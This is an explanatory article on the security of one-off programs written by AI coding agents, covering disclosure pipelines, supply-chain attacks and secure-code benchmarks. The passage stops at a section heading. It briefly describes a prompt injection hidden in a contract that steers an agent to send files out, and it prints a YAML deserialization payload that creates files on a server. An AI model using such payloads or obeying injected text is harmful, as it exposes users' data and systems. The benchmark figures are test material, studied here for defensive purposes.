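# Security review of one-off code written by AI models

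## What one-off generated code is and what can go wrong with it

One-off code is a program that an AI model writes for one person or organisation, and that nobody else runs or reads. It can be ten lines that rename a folder of photographs, or a website with a database and paying customers. Most of the software people rely on has many owners, who run identical copies of it. If someone finds a security flaw in a popular library for reading PDF files, one repair can be used by everybody who has the library. One-off code has no other owners to share repairs with.

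People wrote programs for their own use long before AI, a practice researchers call end-user programming. *Bespoke Visual Assistance* (2026), a study of the tools that blind and low-vision people build with AI, uses Ko and colleagues' definition, in which the program is meant "primarily for personal, rather [than] public use". One-off code may have no human reader, not even the person who asked for it. Professional code is mostly hidden from outsiders too, but a company's private repository often has several programmers who read each other's changes. On GitHub, the largest site for storing and sharing code, 81.5% of contributions in 2025 went to private repositories, according to It's FOSS's *GitHub’s 2025 Report Reveals Some Surprising Developer Trends*.

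The writer is usually a coding agent, an AI model that writes, runs and changes code by itself to carry out a request. Older tools completed a line or a block while a programmer typed. According to *Agentic Much?* (2026), agents differ in the scale of the tasks they take on and in their autonomy. An agent repeatedly reads files, writes or edits code, runs a command, reads the output and picks the next step. Anthropic's *Agentic coding and persistent returns to expertise* (2026), an analysis of about 400,000 sessions with the company's agent Claude Code, found that each user instruction set off around ten such actions on average. Users made about 70% of the decisions on what to do but only 20% of the decisions on how to do it, and a program's security depends mostly on how it is written.

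Vibe coding means describing what software should do and accepting the code an agent writes without reading it. *Understanding the (In)Security of Vibe-Coded Applications* (Deng, Fan and Meng, 2026) contrasts it with ordinary AI-assisted programming, where a developer still reviews the code and answers for the design. Logs do not show whether the developer read the code, so researchers measure how much of it the agent wrote. *SWE-chat* (Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues, 2026) collected almost 18,000 agent sessions from open-source developers who had agreed to share them. It counted a session as vibe coding if the agent wrote more than 99% of the code that the developer finally saved to the project. Overall, 41% of sessions met this threshold, with the share rising from under 20% in February to over 50% in recent months. This is a loose proxy for accepting code unread, because in 37% of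 the sessions counted as vibe coding the user was an "expert nitpicker", the study's term for someone who corrects the agent's output in detail.

Open-source developers are also the wrong group to study if the concern is code that nobody reads. In the survey behind *From Prompting to Verification* (2026), non-developers left more of the work to the AI than professionals did, and agreed more strongly that vibe coding let them build software they could not have built otherwise. People who could not have built the software themselves cannot easily check it by reading the code.

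### How much of it there is

Nobody has counted one-off code, since most of it never reaches a place where anyone could count it. The existing figures are for related things.

Agents' share of code on GitHub is large and growing fast. According to EconoTimes' *More Than 40% of September GitHub Pull Requests* (2026), GitHub put the number of pull requests (proposed changes to a project's code) that began with an agent's draft at 110 million in September 2026. That was more than 40% of the total, up from 17% in March. Independent counts are harder to make. Khosravani and Mockus (2026), in *Detecting AI Coding Agents in Open Source*, searched more than 180 million repositories and found over 320,000 saved changes a month that bore some agent's mark. They call this a lower bound. Searching only for Claude Code's account name would have found just 3.3% of the changes they could trace to it, and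 some agents leave almost no mark. GitHub's figure is more than 300 times as large as theirs. The two cover different months and count different things, but the gap gives a fair idea of how uncertain the numbers are, even for code that people put in a repository.

*Knowledge as Code* (Monperrus, 2026) comes closest to measuring how much agent-written code runs once and disappears. Monperrus calls a program a probe if an agent writes it to find something out and runs it for the answer, often without ever saving it. Across 29,260 records of agents at work, about a quarter of the lines of code belonged to probes, though the rate could be quite different in other corpora. In an example from *Analyzing and Mitigating Cost-Inefficient Behaviors in Coding Agents* (2026), an agent wrote four scripts of 23 to 29 lines to reproduce a single bug in Django, a web framework. The scripts differed by only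 a few lines, but each disappeared after it ran, so the agent had to write the next one from scratch.

Ordinary users also produce code. Anthropic (2026) estimated in its June Economic Index report that about a sixth of conversations in its chat and office-work products end in code or other technical work, such as an app or a script. *The Shift to Agentic AI* (Johnston, Holtz and colleagues, 2026) found that the number of weekly users of OpenAI's agent Codex grew more than fivefold between January and June 2026, with the fastest growth outside software development. The starting point was low. Fewer than 1% of OpenAI's active individual users had used Codex in the preceding 28 days, compared with 17.3% of users on business accounts. None of these figures shows what happened to the code. Anthropic says it cannot tell from its study of Claude Code sessions whether people later used or discarded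 what they made.

Whole applications are easier to count because a few companies host them. Lovable, a Swedish firm, builds web applications from descriptions in ordinary language. Its head of growth, Verna (2026), reports in *How did Lovable grow so fast?* that users start 1.2 million projects a week and that the applications draw more than a billion visits a month. The Next Web reported in 2026 that 80% of the builders are non-technical, based on the company's own unaudited data. Many of the projects must be short, abandoned attempts, though. Deng and colleagues surveyed 9,041 generated applications with public source code and found that about 11% of the web applications were live on the internet.

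### Three cases

What can go wrong depends on where a program runs, how long it lasts and who can reach it. Three cases cover most of the possibilities.

In an example from Anthropic's session study, a lawyer asks an agent to flag missing clauses across a folder of contracts. The agent writes a script and runs it once on the lawyer's laptop, and the lawyer reads the resulting list. An operating system normally gives a program the permissions of the user who starts it, so the script has the lawyer's permissions. Unless something limits it, the script can read every client's files, delete them, or send them anywhere on the internet.

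One-off code can cause harm without an attacker. A script that tidies duplicates can overwrite the signed version of a contract with the draft, and a script that converts documents can upload them to an outside service the lawyer never chose. Run-once programs also affect outside systems more often than readers might expect from the word "script". Monperrus describes an agent that created a real channel on the messaging service Telegram to see what the service's reply looked like.

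An attacker could reach the script through the files it reads. Contracts come from other parties, and one of them could send hostile input, which is data designed to make a program misbehave, such as a document that crashes or hijacks the script's PDF reader. Prompt injection targets the model instead, using text in a web page, file or message that the model wrongly follows as an instruction. For example, if the agent opens a contract to learn its layout and finds a line in white type telling it to send the folder to some address, it may write and run working code that does so. Schneier (2026), in *Cybersecurity in the Age of Instant Software*, thinks it is unclear whether anyone will ever solve prompt injection.

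A **private tool** is a program that its owner keeps and a handful of people use. Lovable's *We just raised $400M in Series C funding* (2026) quotes a director at the software firm Zendesk whose teams built internal training tools and a planning application for themselves. *Vibe coding for clinicians* (2026) discusses doctors with little or no coding experience who build digital health apps. The security department may not know that such tools exist. In *'Now you can have an agent navigate it'*, based on an interview with Lovable's co-founder, Constantin (2026) reported that two-thirds of the Fortune 500 use Lovable, often because staff found it by themselves.

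A private tool often holds a stored key to a larger system, such as the customer database, and acts with that key's permissions no matter who is using it. If the key gives access to everything in that system, a junior employee who opens the tool may be able to see all of it, and so may an intruder who has got into the company's network some other way. Outsiders can also reach the tool indirectly, because it processes what they send. A support request, a supplier's spreadsheet or a contract can all contain hostile input.

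As a private tool ages, it can move from disposable toward durable without anyone deciding that it should. *Disposable Implementations* (2026) reports that the engineer Kanat-Alexander places software on a scale between the two, according to the consequences of failure, the number of people and systems that depend on it, and the costs of rewriting and maintaining it. For example, someone may build a stopgap in an afternoon, then change jobs after the monthly accounts have come to depend on it. Lovable now sells its business customers a feature for cleaning up abandoned apps, so the problem is presumably common.

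**The public application.** Once a generated program is on the internet, anyone can send it requests, and attackers use automated scanners that try addresses regardless of who owns them. The program runs on a server, typically with access to the whole database, and acts on strangers' requests. Often, only its own checks stop one customer from seeing another's data. Deng and colleagues examined live applications and found that a healthcare provider's platform exposed a large volume of customer information because those checks failed. They also found a flaw that let an outsider run commands on the server and take full control of it.

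### The invoice page

Suppose a bookkeeper asks an agent for a website where clients can log in and see their invoices. Invoice 1041 has an address ending in /invoices/1041. The agent writes something like this:

```
def show_invoice(user, invoice_id):
    if not user.logged_in:
        return login_page()
    invoice = database.find_invoice(invoice_id)
    return make_pdf(invoice)
```

The page checks that the visitor has logged in, but not that the requested invoice belongs to them. A client who changes 1041 to 1042 in the browser's address bar gets another client's invoice, and a short program that tries each number in turn gets all of them. One more line of code, refusing any invoice that does not belong to the user, would prevent this.

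That hole is a vulnerability, a flaw that lets someone make a program do something its owner did not intend to allow. The missing line is part of access control, which consists of the rules about which user may see or change which data and the checks that enforce them. Security specialists keep a public catalogue of types of software weakness, the Common Weakness Enumeration, in which each entry has a CWE number. The mistake in the bookkeeper's page is CWE-639, in which a program lets users get past its access rules because it trusts an identifier that they can edit.

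The other public records depend on the code having a name. In the last line of the example, which turns the invoice into a PDF, the agent would probably use an existing library instead of writing that code itself. The library is then a dependency, meaning code from other people that the program needs in order to run. Suppose a researcher working on someone else's system finds a vulnerability in the library. The flaw can get a CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) identifier, a public label for one known vulnerability in one named product or package. A notice called an advisory then lists the vulnerable versions and the version that fixes the flaw. A tool on the bookkeeper's server can compare the installed version with the advisory and raise a warning.

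None of this happens for the missing line in the bookkeeper's page, because the page is not a product, no stranger has a copy, and there is no list of versions for a tool to check. CVE-2025-48757, rated 9.3 out of 10 for severity, is an intermediate case. It concerns the databases behind sites that Lovable generated. Deng and colleagues report that the databases' row-level security, the rules that decide which records each user may read, was too weak, so attackers could get at users' data without logging in. Each site belonged only to its owner, but the vulnerability could be recorded under Lovable's name because Lovable had generated them all.

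The invoice page is faulty code, which does harm that nobody intended. Malicious code works as its author intended, against the interests of the person who runs it. One-off code can contain either. Malicious code can arrive in a dependency if a criminal has taken over the account from which the dependency's author publishes. It can also come from prompt injection, in which a hidden instruction causes an otherwise trustworthy agent to write a malicious program. Adding one line fixes the invoice page, but deleting malicious code after it has run is not enough, because it may already have stolen passwords. A scanner that looks for known malware won't detect the fault in the invoice page.

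Code review can find the flaw in that page more easily than testing can. Testing means running a program on chosen inputs and comparing the results with what they should be. The bookkeeper logs in, opens invoice 1041, sees the right amounts and is satisfied. Anthropic's session study counts passing tests or a user's explicit approval as evidence of success, so by its standards the job went well. A test that logs in as one client and requests another's invoice could expose the flaw, but someone has to think of it first. Code review means reading the program, or having a tool or another model read it, to see what it would allow. A reviewer who knows the pattern will notice the missing line quickly, without needing another client's account.

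The same flaw in a widely used invoicing package would have had more chances to be caught. Some customer would have mistyped a number and complained, or a cautious buyer would have paid for a review, and the fix would then have gone out to everyone, including the bookkeeper. Some protections, such as a login screen or a backup, work just as well for a program with one owner. The remaining question is which protections depend on other people having the same code, and what could replace them when nobody else has it.

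## How open-source software is checked, and how well

Anyone may read, copy and change the source code of open-source software. Programmers usually get it as packages, ready-made pieces of code that they download from a public registry such as npm (for the language JavaScript) or PyPI (for Python). The library that makes the bookkeeper's PDFs would be one such package. Few users read the packages they install. They rely on other people to find the flaws, fix them and tell everyone who has a copy.

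### From a report to an alert

A flaw in React, a library from Meta for building web pages, was reported, fixed and disclosed within four days. Lachlan Davidson reported it privately on 29 November 2025 through Meta's bug bounty, a scheme that pays outsiders for finding flaws. An attacker could send a specially made request to a server that used certain React features and run commands on it without logging in. According to React (2025), Meta's researchers confirmed the flaw the next day. By 1 December the developers had a fix and were testing it with hosting companies, which added temporary defences. On 3 December React released the repaired versions and disclosed the flaw as CVE-2025-55182, with the maximum severity score of 10.

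Secrecy gave the developers time to write a fix before most attackers knew about the flaw. After disclosure, users had to install the fix before attackers could exploit the flaw on their systems. By 5 December, the US government's cybersecurity agency had added it to its list of flaws that attackers were already using, according to GCVE (2026), a public vulnerability database.

The people who needed the fix had to find out that they needed it. Schaumann (2025), in *CVE-2025-55182*, told a security mailing list which packages were affected and in which versions, and an advisory holds the same facts in a form that a program can read. On the user's side, a project normally has a file listing every package it depends on, with the exact version. GitHub reads these files, and when a new advisory arrives, its tool Dependabot compares it with all of them:

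```
advisory:  react-server-dom-webpack  19.0.0, 19.1.0, 19.1.1, 19.2.0
project:   react-server-dom-webpack  19.1.1
result:    alert (upgrade to 19.1.2)
```

Dependabot bases the alert only on the package's name and version. A programmer who had copied React's faulty function into their own file would get no alert, and a project that lists the package but never uses it would still get one.

Ambiguous package names cause a lot of trouble in vulnerability reports. GitHub's *Inside the Advisory Database and what happens when vulnerability volume breaks records* (2026) explains that if a report mentions a package called "foo", staff may have to work out whether this is foo on npm, python-foo on PyPI or an unrelated foo on a third registry. If they enter the wrong name, affected users may never hear of the flaw.

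Copies that have lost their label are harder still. curl, a tool and library for transferring data over the internet, is part of a vast number of other products. In *The pressure* (Stenberg, 2026), curl's lead developer repeats an estimate of perhaps thirty billion installations. Stenberg (2026) describes a meeting with a large American power company that had found a vulnerable copy of curl's library in a Windows system folder and wanted help upgrading it. He had to refuse because another application had put the file there, and only the people who built that copy could replace it without risking a crash. The company's scanner could detect that file, but many applications compile the library into their own program, which leaves no separate file to find.

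Alerts can also arrive late, because GitHub's staff check an advisory before GitHub sends alerts about it. Help Net Security's *In GitHub’s advisory pipeline, some advisories move faster than others* gives the median time from a fix to that check, for advisories published after mid-2022. It was two days if the project's maintainers had published the advisory on GitHub, and 28 days if it came from the US National Vulnerability Database. During the wait, attackers can work out the flaw from the published fix, while many users don't know they need the fix.

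### What a package's reputation proves

Advisories cover only flaws that somebody has found. Before installing a package, a programmer can also look at how many people use it, who maintains it and how its release was made.

A download count is only a rough measure of how much a package is used. A company's build system may fetch the same package hundreds of times a day, and anyone can write a short program to inflate the count. A package's past popularity also doesn't show that its next release is safe. Willison (2026), a programmer who logs attacks on packages, describes how Axios, a JavaScript package with 101 million weekly downloads, had releases in March 2026 that installed malware.

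Stars on GitHub, which work like "likes" on social media, are sold in batches of 50 or 100. *Six Million (Suspected) Fake Stars on GitHub* (He, Kapravelos and colleagues, 2024) searched for accounts that had starred one repository and then become inactive, and for groups of at least 50 accounts that had starred the same repositories within a month. It found six million suspected fake stars from July 2019 to December 2024, and 18,617 repositories that had apparently run a campaign to collect them. In July 2024, the worst month, 16.66% of all repositories that gained 50 or more stars were linked to these campaigns.

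The method cannot prove that any particular star is fake, but by January 2025 about 90% of the campaign repositories had disappeared from GitHub, compared with 5% of a random sample. Most of the missing repositories had names suggesting pirated software, game cheats or cryptocurrency bots, and He and colleagues think they were probably malware. Only 229 of the campaign repositories had packages in a registry, and about 70% of those packages had no other package depending on them. Fake stars therefore mainly endanger people who download programs directly from GitHub.

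A maintainer's good record is harder to buy, but an attacker can steal the maintainer's account. Willison summarises the cryptographer Filippo Valsorda's survey of 18 attacks in 2024 and 2025 that put malware into existing open-source projects. Five began with phishing (tricking a maintainer into giving up a password), and about five more with stolen credentials that stayed valid for a long time. In three, the maintainer had handed control to someone who proved untrustworthy. Four exploited automated build processes, and in one the attacker bought a web domain that a maintainer had let expire.

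OpenSSF Scorecard, the best-known automated tool for rating how open-source projects are run, gives scores from 0 to 10 for practices such as requiring a second person to approve each change. A high score shows that the project follows good practices, though a dishonest maintainer could approve their own changes from a second account.

A signature on a release proves that the holder of a secret key approved the file and that nobody has altered it since. Keys are easy to lose or steal. Sigstore, a free service that the Open Source Security Foundation maintains, avoids this problem by using certificates that expire within minutes. Each certificate ties the signature to an identity, such as an email account or a project's build process, and Sigstore records it in a public log.

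Build provenance is a record of how a file was built. SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) is a standard for such records. Its first level requires only that the record exist. The second requires a hosted build service to sign it. The third also requires the service to keep each build from tampering with others or reaching the signing keys. Willison published one of his packages with build provenance, and its entry in the Sigstore log lists the repository, the build instructions and the exact version of the source code, so anyone can check that the package on PyPI came from the code on GitHub.

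Google's OSS Rebuild project produces similar evidence after packages are published, by rebuilding popular ones from source and comparing the results with the published versions. Willison counted 9,513 packages in its list in July 2025. That is a small share of all packages; PyPI alone gains 700 to 800 new projects a day.

Provenance records can be used to detect a package that does not match its source, but not to tell whether the source is safe. The bookkeeper's invoice page could have a valid provenance record and still show every client's invoices to every other client. An attacker who gets into the build process, as in four of Valsorda's 18 cases, may also be able to produce a valid record for a malicious file.

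### Do many eyes find the bugs?

In 1997 the programmer Eric Raymond wrote that "given enough eyeballs, all bugs are shallow", and open-source developers have relied on the idea ever since. The arithmetic behind it is sound. Suppose each user of a package has a one-in-a-thousand chance of noticing a certain flaw within a year. If 10,000 users act independently, the chance that someone notices is 1 − 0.999^10,000, or more than 99.99%. But if only ten of them ever read the code and the flaw never shows in ordinary use, the chance is 1 − 0.999^10, or about 1%. The chance of catching such a flaw depends on how many people read the code, and that number can be tiny even for a package with a million users.

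The evidence suggests that open-source code often goes unreviewed and that flaws can remain in it for years. *Are Your Dependencies Code Reviewed?* (Imtiaz and Williams, 2022) examined the ten latest updates of the 1,000 most downloaded packages in each of four registries, and found that only 9% of the packages had had all the code in those updates reviewed. *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?* (Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues, 2022) estimated that vulnerabilities in large open-source projects survived for about four years on average. The average was around two years for Chromium, the basis of Google's Chrome browser, and seven for the encryption library OpenSSL. Both projects are among the most closely watched, and the averages exclude flaws that nobody has found yet. *Curl Fixes a 25-Year-Old Bug in Its Largest CVE Release Yet* (Paganini, 2026) reported that curl's maintainers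 fixed a vulnerability in June 2026 that had been in the code for 25 years.

Both sides of the argument cite the xz backdoor of 2024 as evidence. xz is a compression tool found on almost every Linux system, and for years one tired volunteer maintained it. In 2021 someone using the name Jia Tan began sending him useful improvements. Other accounts, probably run by the same people, complained about slow progress and pressed the volunteer to accept help. By 2023 Jia Tan was publishing the releases.

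Version 5.6.0, released in February 2024, contained a backdoor that let the holder of a secret key run commands on affected machines through SSH, the standard system for remote login. Jia Tan hid the malicious code in files that looked like test data. The script that unpacked it was in the release archive but not in the public repository, where reviewers would normally look.

Andres Freund, an engineer at Microsoft, noticed that logins on a test machine were taking about half a second longer than they should. He traced the delay to xz and published his findings on 29 March, five weeks after the release. The backdoor had reached test versions of several Linux systems but hardly any of the stable ones that companies run.

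Freund could trace the delay because he had the source code, and his one report protected everybody. But he was measuring the speed of something else and had no plan to review xz. Reputation gave no protection, because Jia Tan had more than two years of real contributions and signed the releases with a genuine key. Provenance might have exposed the extra script in the archive, but a maintainer could have added the script to the repository too. Overall, the evidence that many eyes help is much stronger for what happens after someone finds a flaw than for whether anyone will find it.

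### The LiteLLM attack of March 2026

LiteLLM is a Python package that connects programs to many companies' AI models, so the computers that run it often hold valuable keys. *Hardening Your LLM Dependency Supply Chain* (2026), from Mozilla.ai, which offers a rival product, puts LiteLLM's downloads at more than 95 million a month.

The attack started with Trivy, a security scanner. A group known as TeamPCP broke into the Trivy project and then, according to Datadog Security Labs, into several others. LiteLLM ran Trivy as part of its automated build, and LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) gives this as the attackers' likely way in. The attackers were then able to publish on PyPI under a maintainer's account.

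At 10:39 UTC on 24 March the attackers uploaded version 1.82.7 of litellm, whose malware ran when a program loaded one particular part of the package. Thirteen minutes later they uploaded 1.82.8. *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8* (Willison, 2026) explains that this version included a type of file that Python runs automatically, so installing the package was enough to set off the malware. It collected passwords, cloud credentials, SSH keys and cryptocurrency wallets, and sent them to the attackers. The source code on GitHub stayed clean throughout, so anyone who reviewed it would have found nothing wrong.

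The attack was discovered because of a bug in the malware. The automatic file started a new copy of Python, which ran the file again, and so on until the machine crashed. Callum McMahon of the forecasting company FutureSearch investigated with help from Claude, Anthropic's AI model, and reported the attack to PyPI. Warning other users was harder because, according to FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026), hundreds of bots flooded the public discussion on GitHub and someone using the owner's account closed it as "not planned".

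Accounts differ on how long the malicious versions were available. FutureSearch's *LiteLLM Hack* gives 46 minutes and 46,996 downloads, and LiteLLM says about 40 minutes. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) gives 2 hours 32 minutes and more than 119,000 downloads. PyPI's figures are more believable because it runs the registry and received its first report 1 hour 19 minutes after the upload, about half an hour after it would have blocked the package if the shorter figures were right.

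Whether an installation fetched the malware depended largely on how it specified the version. A project can pin a package, meaning that it accepts one exact version, or it can accept any version above some minimum and get the newest. FutureSearch checked all 2,337 packages on PyPI that listed LiteLLM as a direct dependency:

| Versions of LiteLLM accepted | Packages | Share | Could install the malware |
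|---|---|---|---|
| Any | 283 | 12% | Yes |
| Anything above a minimum | 1,388 | 59% | Yes |
| A range that included 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 | 383 | 16% | Yes |
| A range that stopped short of them | 74 | 3% | No |
| One exact, safe version | 209 | 9% | No |

Of the packages that depended directly on LiteLLM, 88% were unprotected. Packages that depended on it only through another package were not counted. PyPI estimates that 40–50% of all LiteLLM installations were fetching the newest available version.

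PyPI now recommends a cooldown, a setting that refuses any release less than, say, three days old. This would have blocked the bad versions of LiteLLM and Telnyx while they were available. The same attackers hit Telnyx three days after LiteLLM, and it was exposed for 3 hours 42 minutes. Cooldowns also delay security fixes, so PyPI advises combining them with alerts that let urgent updates through. They work only if other people install the new version first and one of them notices a problem, and a one-off program has no other users to do this before its owner runs it.

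### AI bug-finding and the flood of reports

In 2026 AI models began reviewing much of the open-source code that people had not read. The curl project received so many worthless AI-written reports during 2025 that it stopped paying for vulnerability reports on 1 February 2026. By April, according to *High-Quality Chaos* (Stenberg, 2026), the junk was no longer a problem, but reports were arriving at about twice the 2025 rate, nearly all of them made with AI. About 15–16% described real vulnerabilities, a share at least as high as before the AI era. Stenberg expected close to 50 confirmed vulnerabilities for the year, but by November he had counted 81 (*curl on OSS-Scanner*).

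Maintainers have to deal with all of this. The curl maintainers took July off from vulnerability reports, and Stenberg called it possibly the project's best decision in a long while. In October they started handling all but the most serious flaws in public, hoping outsiders would help, though this gives attackers slightly more time to exploit them.

In early November a free scanning service from Anthropic sent curl 45 suspected vulnerabilities at once. According to Stenberg, the maintainers confirmed five. Another 36 were ordinary bugs, three were not bugs, and one was wrong in a way that meant its suggested fix would have created the vulnerability it described. The maintainers therefore had 41 problems to fix, many more than the five vulnerabilities. The same service had earlier found the most serious of the 22 vulnerabilities that curl fixed in its October release, a memory error that could,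 in rare conditions, let a malicious server run code on the user's machine.

Stenberg asked other open-source projects on social media, and people from more than two dozen, including the Linux kernel, Firefox and Python, reported the same trend. Private vulnerability reports on GitHub rose from about 550 a week in January to over 3,000 a week for most of May. *Agents on the Patch Path* (Segal, Segal and colleagues, 2026) counted 10,492 advisories that GitHub had reviewed and published in 2026 by 23 September, compared with fewer than 3,700 in each of the three previous years.

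AI is also helping to write the fixes. Between July and September, 6–10% of each month's advisories cited a code change with a visible trace of a coding agent, which is again a lower bound.

Human review has not kept pace. Segal and colleagues found that the median time GitHub took to review an advisory after a maintainer published it grew from 0.4 days in January to 41.4 days in September, so many users will have gone weeks without an automatic alert about a flaw that was already public. Attackers can run the same tools, as Stenberg points out, without waiting for anyone's approval.

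The large number of discoveries partly counts against the many-eyes claim and partly supports it. Many flaws had remained in code that anyone could have read, but they were found quickly once the code was read closely. Still, a single clean result is weak evidence that code is secure. Paganini reports that Anthropic's model Mythos had found only one vulnerability in curl by May, after which the security firm Aisle and others found 18 more.

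### What sharing saves

Sharing code divides the work of reviewing and fixing it among many users, as an example with invented numbers shows. Suppose an invoicing package has 10,000 users. A careful review takes 40 hours and finds the missing access check. Preparing the fix, the advisory and the new release takes another 10 hours. Each user then spends three minutes installing the update, or 500 hours in all. The total is 550 hours, or 3.3 minutes per user.

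Now suppose that each of the 10,000 users instead has a separate invoicing program written by an agent. These programs are simpler, so a review takes only two hours. If 30% of them have the flaw and each repair takes an hour, the total is 20,000 hours of review plus 3,000 of repairs. That is 2.3 hours per user, about 42 times as much work as for the shared package. At $100 an hour, the cost per user is $230, compared with $5.50 for the shared package.

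One worried customer can also pay for a review that benefits everyone who uses the same program. When each customer has a separate program, an owner who never thinks about security gets no review.

Upkeep multiplies in the same way, because anyone who replaces a dependency with generated code, as some people now propose, has to maintain that code alone. In autumn 2026, two AI-written versions of curl appeared in Rust, a language that prevents many memory errors. One reportedly cost $8,600 to produce. Stenberg notes that curl's own developers fixed a little over 200 bugs in the roughly three weeks the agents took, and that neither copy had those fixes. He also estimates that Rust would have prevented only 14 of the 81 vulnerabilities confirmed in 2026.

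The comparison depends heavily on the price of a review. Two hours of an expert's time is too expensive for most one-off programs, but a model can read a short program for far less. In the example, separate programs would cost no more than the shared package if someone could find and repair the flaws in each for $5.50.

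## Tests of whether coding agents write secure code

The 30% flaw rate in the invoicing example was hypothetical. Researchers test how often agents leave such flaws by giving them tasks in which a particular flaw is easy to make, then attacking the code they write.

### How a test works

A modern test imitates a user who wants working software and never mentions security. The bookkeeper's request for an invoice site would make a good task. The agent works until it decides it has finished. The testers then run two sets of tests that the agent has not seen. Functional tests check that the program does its job, for example that a client can open invoice 1041. Security tests attack the running program, for example by logging in as a different client and requesting the same invoice.

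An agent could pass every security test by writing a program that does nothing, since nobody can steal an invoice from a page that never loads. The main result is therefore usually the joint pass rate:

```
joint pass rate = tasks that pass both sets of tests / all tasks
```

Suppose an agent attempts 100 tasks, 90 of its programs work, and 25 of those also withstand the attacks. The joint pass rate is 25%. The 65 programs that work but are vulnerable are the dangerous ones, because a user who tries them out will be satisfied. A successful attack proves that a program has a flaw, but some of the 25 that withstood the attacks may also have flaws that nobody tested for.

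Early tests were simpler. *Asleep at the Keyboard?* (2021) studied GitHub Copilot, which then only completed code as a programmer typed. It set up 89 situations that invited a dangerous weakness, checked the 1,689 resulting programs by static analysis (using a tool to search source code without running it) and by hand, and found about 40% vulnerable. BaxBench (2025) asked models to write the whole server side of a web application and attacked it while it ran. The attacks succeeded against about half of the working programs that each model wrote, according to Andročec (2026) in *Vibe Coding and Web Application Security*.

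In *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2025) tested agents inside existing projects. Their benchmark, SusVibes, consists of 186 requests for new features in open-source software. For each request, a human programmer had previously written vulnerable code. An agent using the model Claude 4 Sonnet produced working code for 57% of the requests and secure code for 11.8%.

### The Last Secure Code Benchmark

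The broadest test so far is *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, October 2026), which uses 150 real vulnerabilities in seven programming languages. Of these, 115 were public CVEs, and security experts recreated the other 35 from flaws in their own companies' Java software. For each vulnerability, the researchers cut the flawed code out of the project and asked an agent to write it again. They repeated this with three amounts of missing code, making 450 tasks: a function or two (155 lines on average), whole files (1,782 lines), and a large part of the project (4,120 lines).

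The written specifications had to fit both the vulnerable original and the repaired version, without requiring the flaw or revealing the fix. The researchers also required the original code to pass the functional tests and fail the security tests, and the repaired code to pass both. Some older security tests only searched the source code for certain words, so an agent could have passed them by writing those words in a comment. To catch this, Wu and colleagues pasted each fix into the vulnerable code as comments, which do not affect how a program runs, and dropped any task whose security tests then passed.

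Six agents each made one attempt at every task, without internet access:

| Model | Works | Works and is secure | Secure at all three sizes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 91.1% | 25.1% | 12.0% |
| GPT-5.6-Sol | 89.1% | 24.7% | 8.0% |
| Qwen3.8-Max | 89.3% | 22.0% | 8.0% |
| GLM-5.3 | 87.1% | 21.3% | 7.3% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 73.6% | 18.0% | 6.7% |
| Kimi-K3 | 91.3% | 16.4% | 2.0% |

The last column is a share of the 150 vulnerabilities, and the others are shares of the 450 tasks. Claude Fable 5, the best model, passed both sets of tests on 113 tasks. On another 297, its code worked but was vulnerable. DeepSeek-V4-Pro's rate of passing both was low mostly because its code often did not work. On the 271 tasks where all six models wrote working code, the code was secure 25–28% of the time for five models, including DeepSeek, and 17% of the time for Kimi-K3.

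The type of weakness made much more difference than the choice of model:

| Weakness | What secure code has to do | Joint pass rate, all models |
|---|---|---|
| Memory safety | Stay within the memory set aside for the data | 34.3% |
| Path and file handling | Keep to the intended folder and file types | 24.3% |
| Injection | Stop input from running as commands or code | 23.9% |
| Deserialization | Rebuild only harmless objects from stored data | 19.0% |
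| Access control | Check who may do what | 18.3% |
| Input validation and limits | Reject malformed or excessive input | 14.6% |
| Server-side request forgery | Refuse to fetch from forbidden places | 2.4% |
| Information exposure | Keep secrets out of the output | 0.7% |

Some of these rates rest on only seven or eight vulnerabilities, but the same categories ranked at the top and bottom for every model. Wu and colleagues offer a convincing explanation. A programmer who writes a careful loop checks where the list ends, which also prevents a memory error. But an agent cannot learn from the function it is writing whether the server may read a certain file for a stranger, because that depends on policy.

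In one of the information-exposure tasks, the agents had to restore nine lines of settings for syft, a tool that lists the components of a piece of software. One setting was a password. All six agents formatted it like the settings around it, so syft printed the password in its reports, which users often publish. Claude Fable 5 checked that the setting appeared in the reports and described this as correct behaviour.

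The benchmark includes seven cases of CWE-639, the flaw in the bookkeeper's invoice page. The agents wrote working code in 98.4% of their attempts at these cases, and code that was both working and secure in 19.8%. So about four in five of the working programs had the flaw.

Results were not clearly better or worse when agents wrote more code. Averaged over the six models, the joint rate was 21.7% for functions, 19.4% for files and 22.7% for large parts of a project. From the smallest size to the largest, GPT-5.6-Sol's rate rose from 20.0% to 30.7%. DeepSeek-V4-Pro's fell from 22.7% to 16.0%, mainly because more of its code failed to work, although Wu and colleagues describe the rate as flat or rising for every model. One possible reason for a rise is that an agent filling a small gap tends to follow the surrounding code and reproduce the original vulnerable design, while an agent writing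 the whole module chooses its own design. If so, the largest size is the best guide to one-off programs, which agents usually write from scratch.

### The YAML importer

One of the deserialization tasks shows how an agent can test its work thoroughly and still miss the flaw. The project is a Java platform for managing other programs' settings. The missing file exports those settings as a ZIP archive of files in YAML, a common text format for settings, and imports such archives. According to the specification, the importer should parse each entry "as YAML into a mapping", meaning a list of names and values, but the agent could choose the parser.

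Kimi-K3 read eleven related files, then wrote and compiled a 207-line class. Its own tests showed that the importer reported success on a corrupt archive without importing anything. Kimi-K3 fixed this, extended its tests to 33 checks, and submitted the code after they all passed. The code passed all 14 hidden functional tests but failed all four security tests.

The fault was in one short call, `new Yaml().load(text)`. By default, the parser in this project accepts tags that name a Java class, and creates an object of that class while reading the file. An uploaded file could therefore contain lines like these:

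```
timeout: 30                                  # an ordinary setting
log: !!java.io.FileWriter ["/tmp/marker"]    # creates a file on the server
```

The testers used such tags to create files on the server and, in one test, to make the server contact a machine they controlled. The same library has a safer option, SafeConstructor, which rejects these tags and reads ordinary settings just as well. Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6-Sol used it and passed both sets of tests. Qwen3.8-Max and GLM-5.3 made the same choice as Kimi-K3. DeepSeek-V4-Pro submitted a file that did not compile.

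None of Kimi-K3's 33 checks used a malicious file. The owner of a private tool would be even less likely to test it with one.

### From test scores to ordinary programs

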